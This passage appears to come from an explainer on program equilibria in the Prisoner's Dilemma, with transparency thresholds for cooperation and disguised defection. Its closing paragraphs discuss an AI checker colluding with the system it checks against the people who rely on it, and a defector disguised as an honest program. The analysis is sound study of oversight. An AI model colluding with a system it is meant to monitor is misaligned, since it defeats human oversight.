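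Their central theorem assumes perfect disguise, meaning that each player can always switch to a program that looks the same to the opponent but makes whatever move the player wants. The theorem covers equilibria in which nobody picks a program at random, and it shows that programs can achieve nothing in these equilibria that players couldn't achieve by choosing moves directly. In the Prisoner's Dilemma, the only such result is mutual defection. Our formula gives the same result. If disguised and honest programs look identical, the reader flags both equally often, so d equals f. The condition then holds only if both are 100%, which means everyone defects.

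Less extreme cases require a measure of how much information a program has about its opponent. Duclaux and colleagues define transparency as the share of the uncertainty about the opponent's identity that this information removes on average. It is 0 if the information reveals nothing about the opponent's identity and 1 if it identifies the opponent exactly. With eight possible opponents, a transparency of 0.48 is roughly like narrowing them down to three.

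They tested two kinds of imperfect information. One confuses programs that act alike, and the other confuses programs whose code looks alike. The table shows the lowest transparency at which full cooperation was an equilibrium:

| Caution | Confuses programs that act alike | Confuses programs that look alike |
|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 0.14 | 0.07 |
| 0.6 | 0.29 | 0.20 |
| 0.7 | 0.44 | 0.37 |
| 0.8 | 0.48 | 0.57 |
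| 0.9 | 0.66 | 0.79 |
| 1.0 | 1.00 | 1.00 |

Every simulated population evolved to full cooperation at or above these levels, and none did below them. With caution at 0.8 and information that confuses programs that act alike with one another, everyone defected in every equilibrium at a transparency of 0.47, but full cooperation became possible at 0.48.

These exact thresholds depend on the small set of programs and on the answer to the unsolved problem about proof length. If the relevant proofs do fit within the limit, cooperation still appears at high transparency, but without a single threshold. The payoffs (3, 2, 0 and −1) also favored honesty. By our formula, a reader with no false alarms would need a detection rate of only 33% in that game.

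Duclaux and colleagues were mainly worried about too much cooperation. An AI system that is supposed to check another may instead collude with it against the people who rely on the check. From that point of view, the possibility of hidden defection is useful, because systems that cannot verify each other's behavior have less reason to collude.

The column for programs that look alike is closer to underhanded code, where a tiny change in the text reverses the behavior, but none of the eight programs was designed to deceive by imitating another. If an author added a program that defects but looks exactly like an honest one, a program facing either of them could be only 50% sure that its opponent was honest, even with otherwise perfect information. The modified DupocBot would defect against both if its caution were above 0.5. Otherwise it would cooperate with both, and the imitation would exploit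 it.
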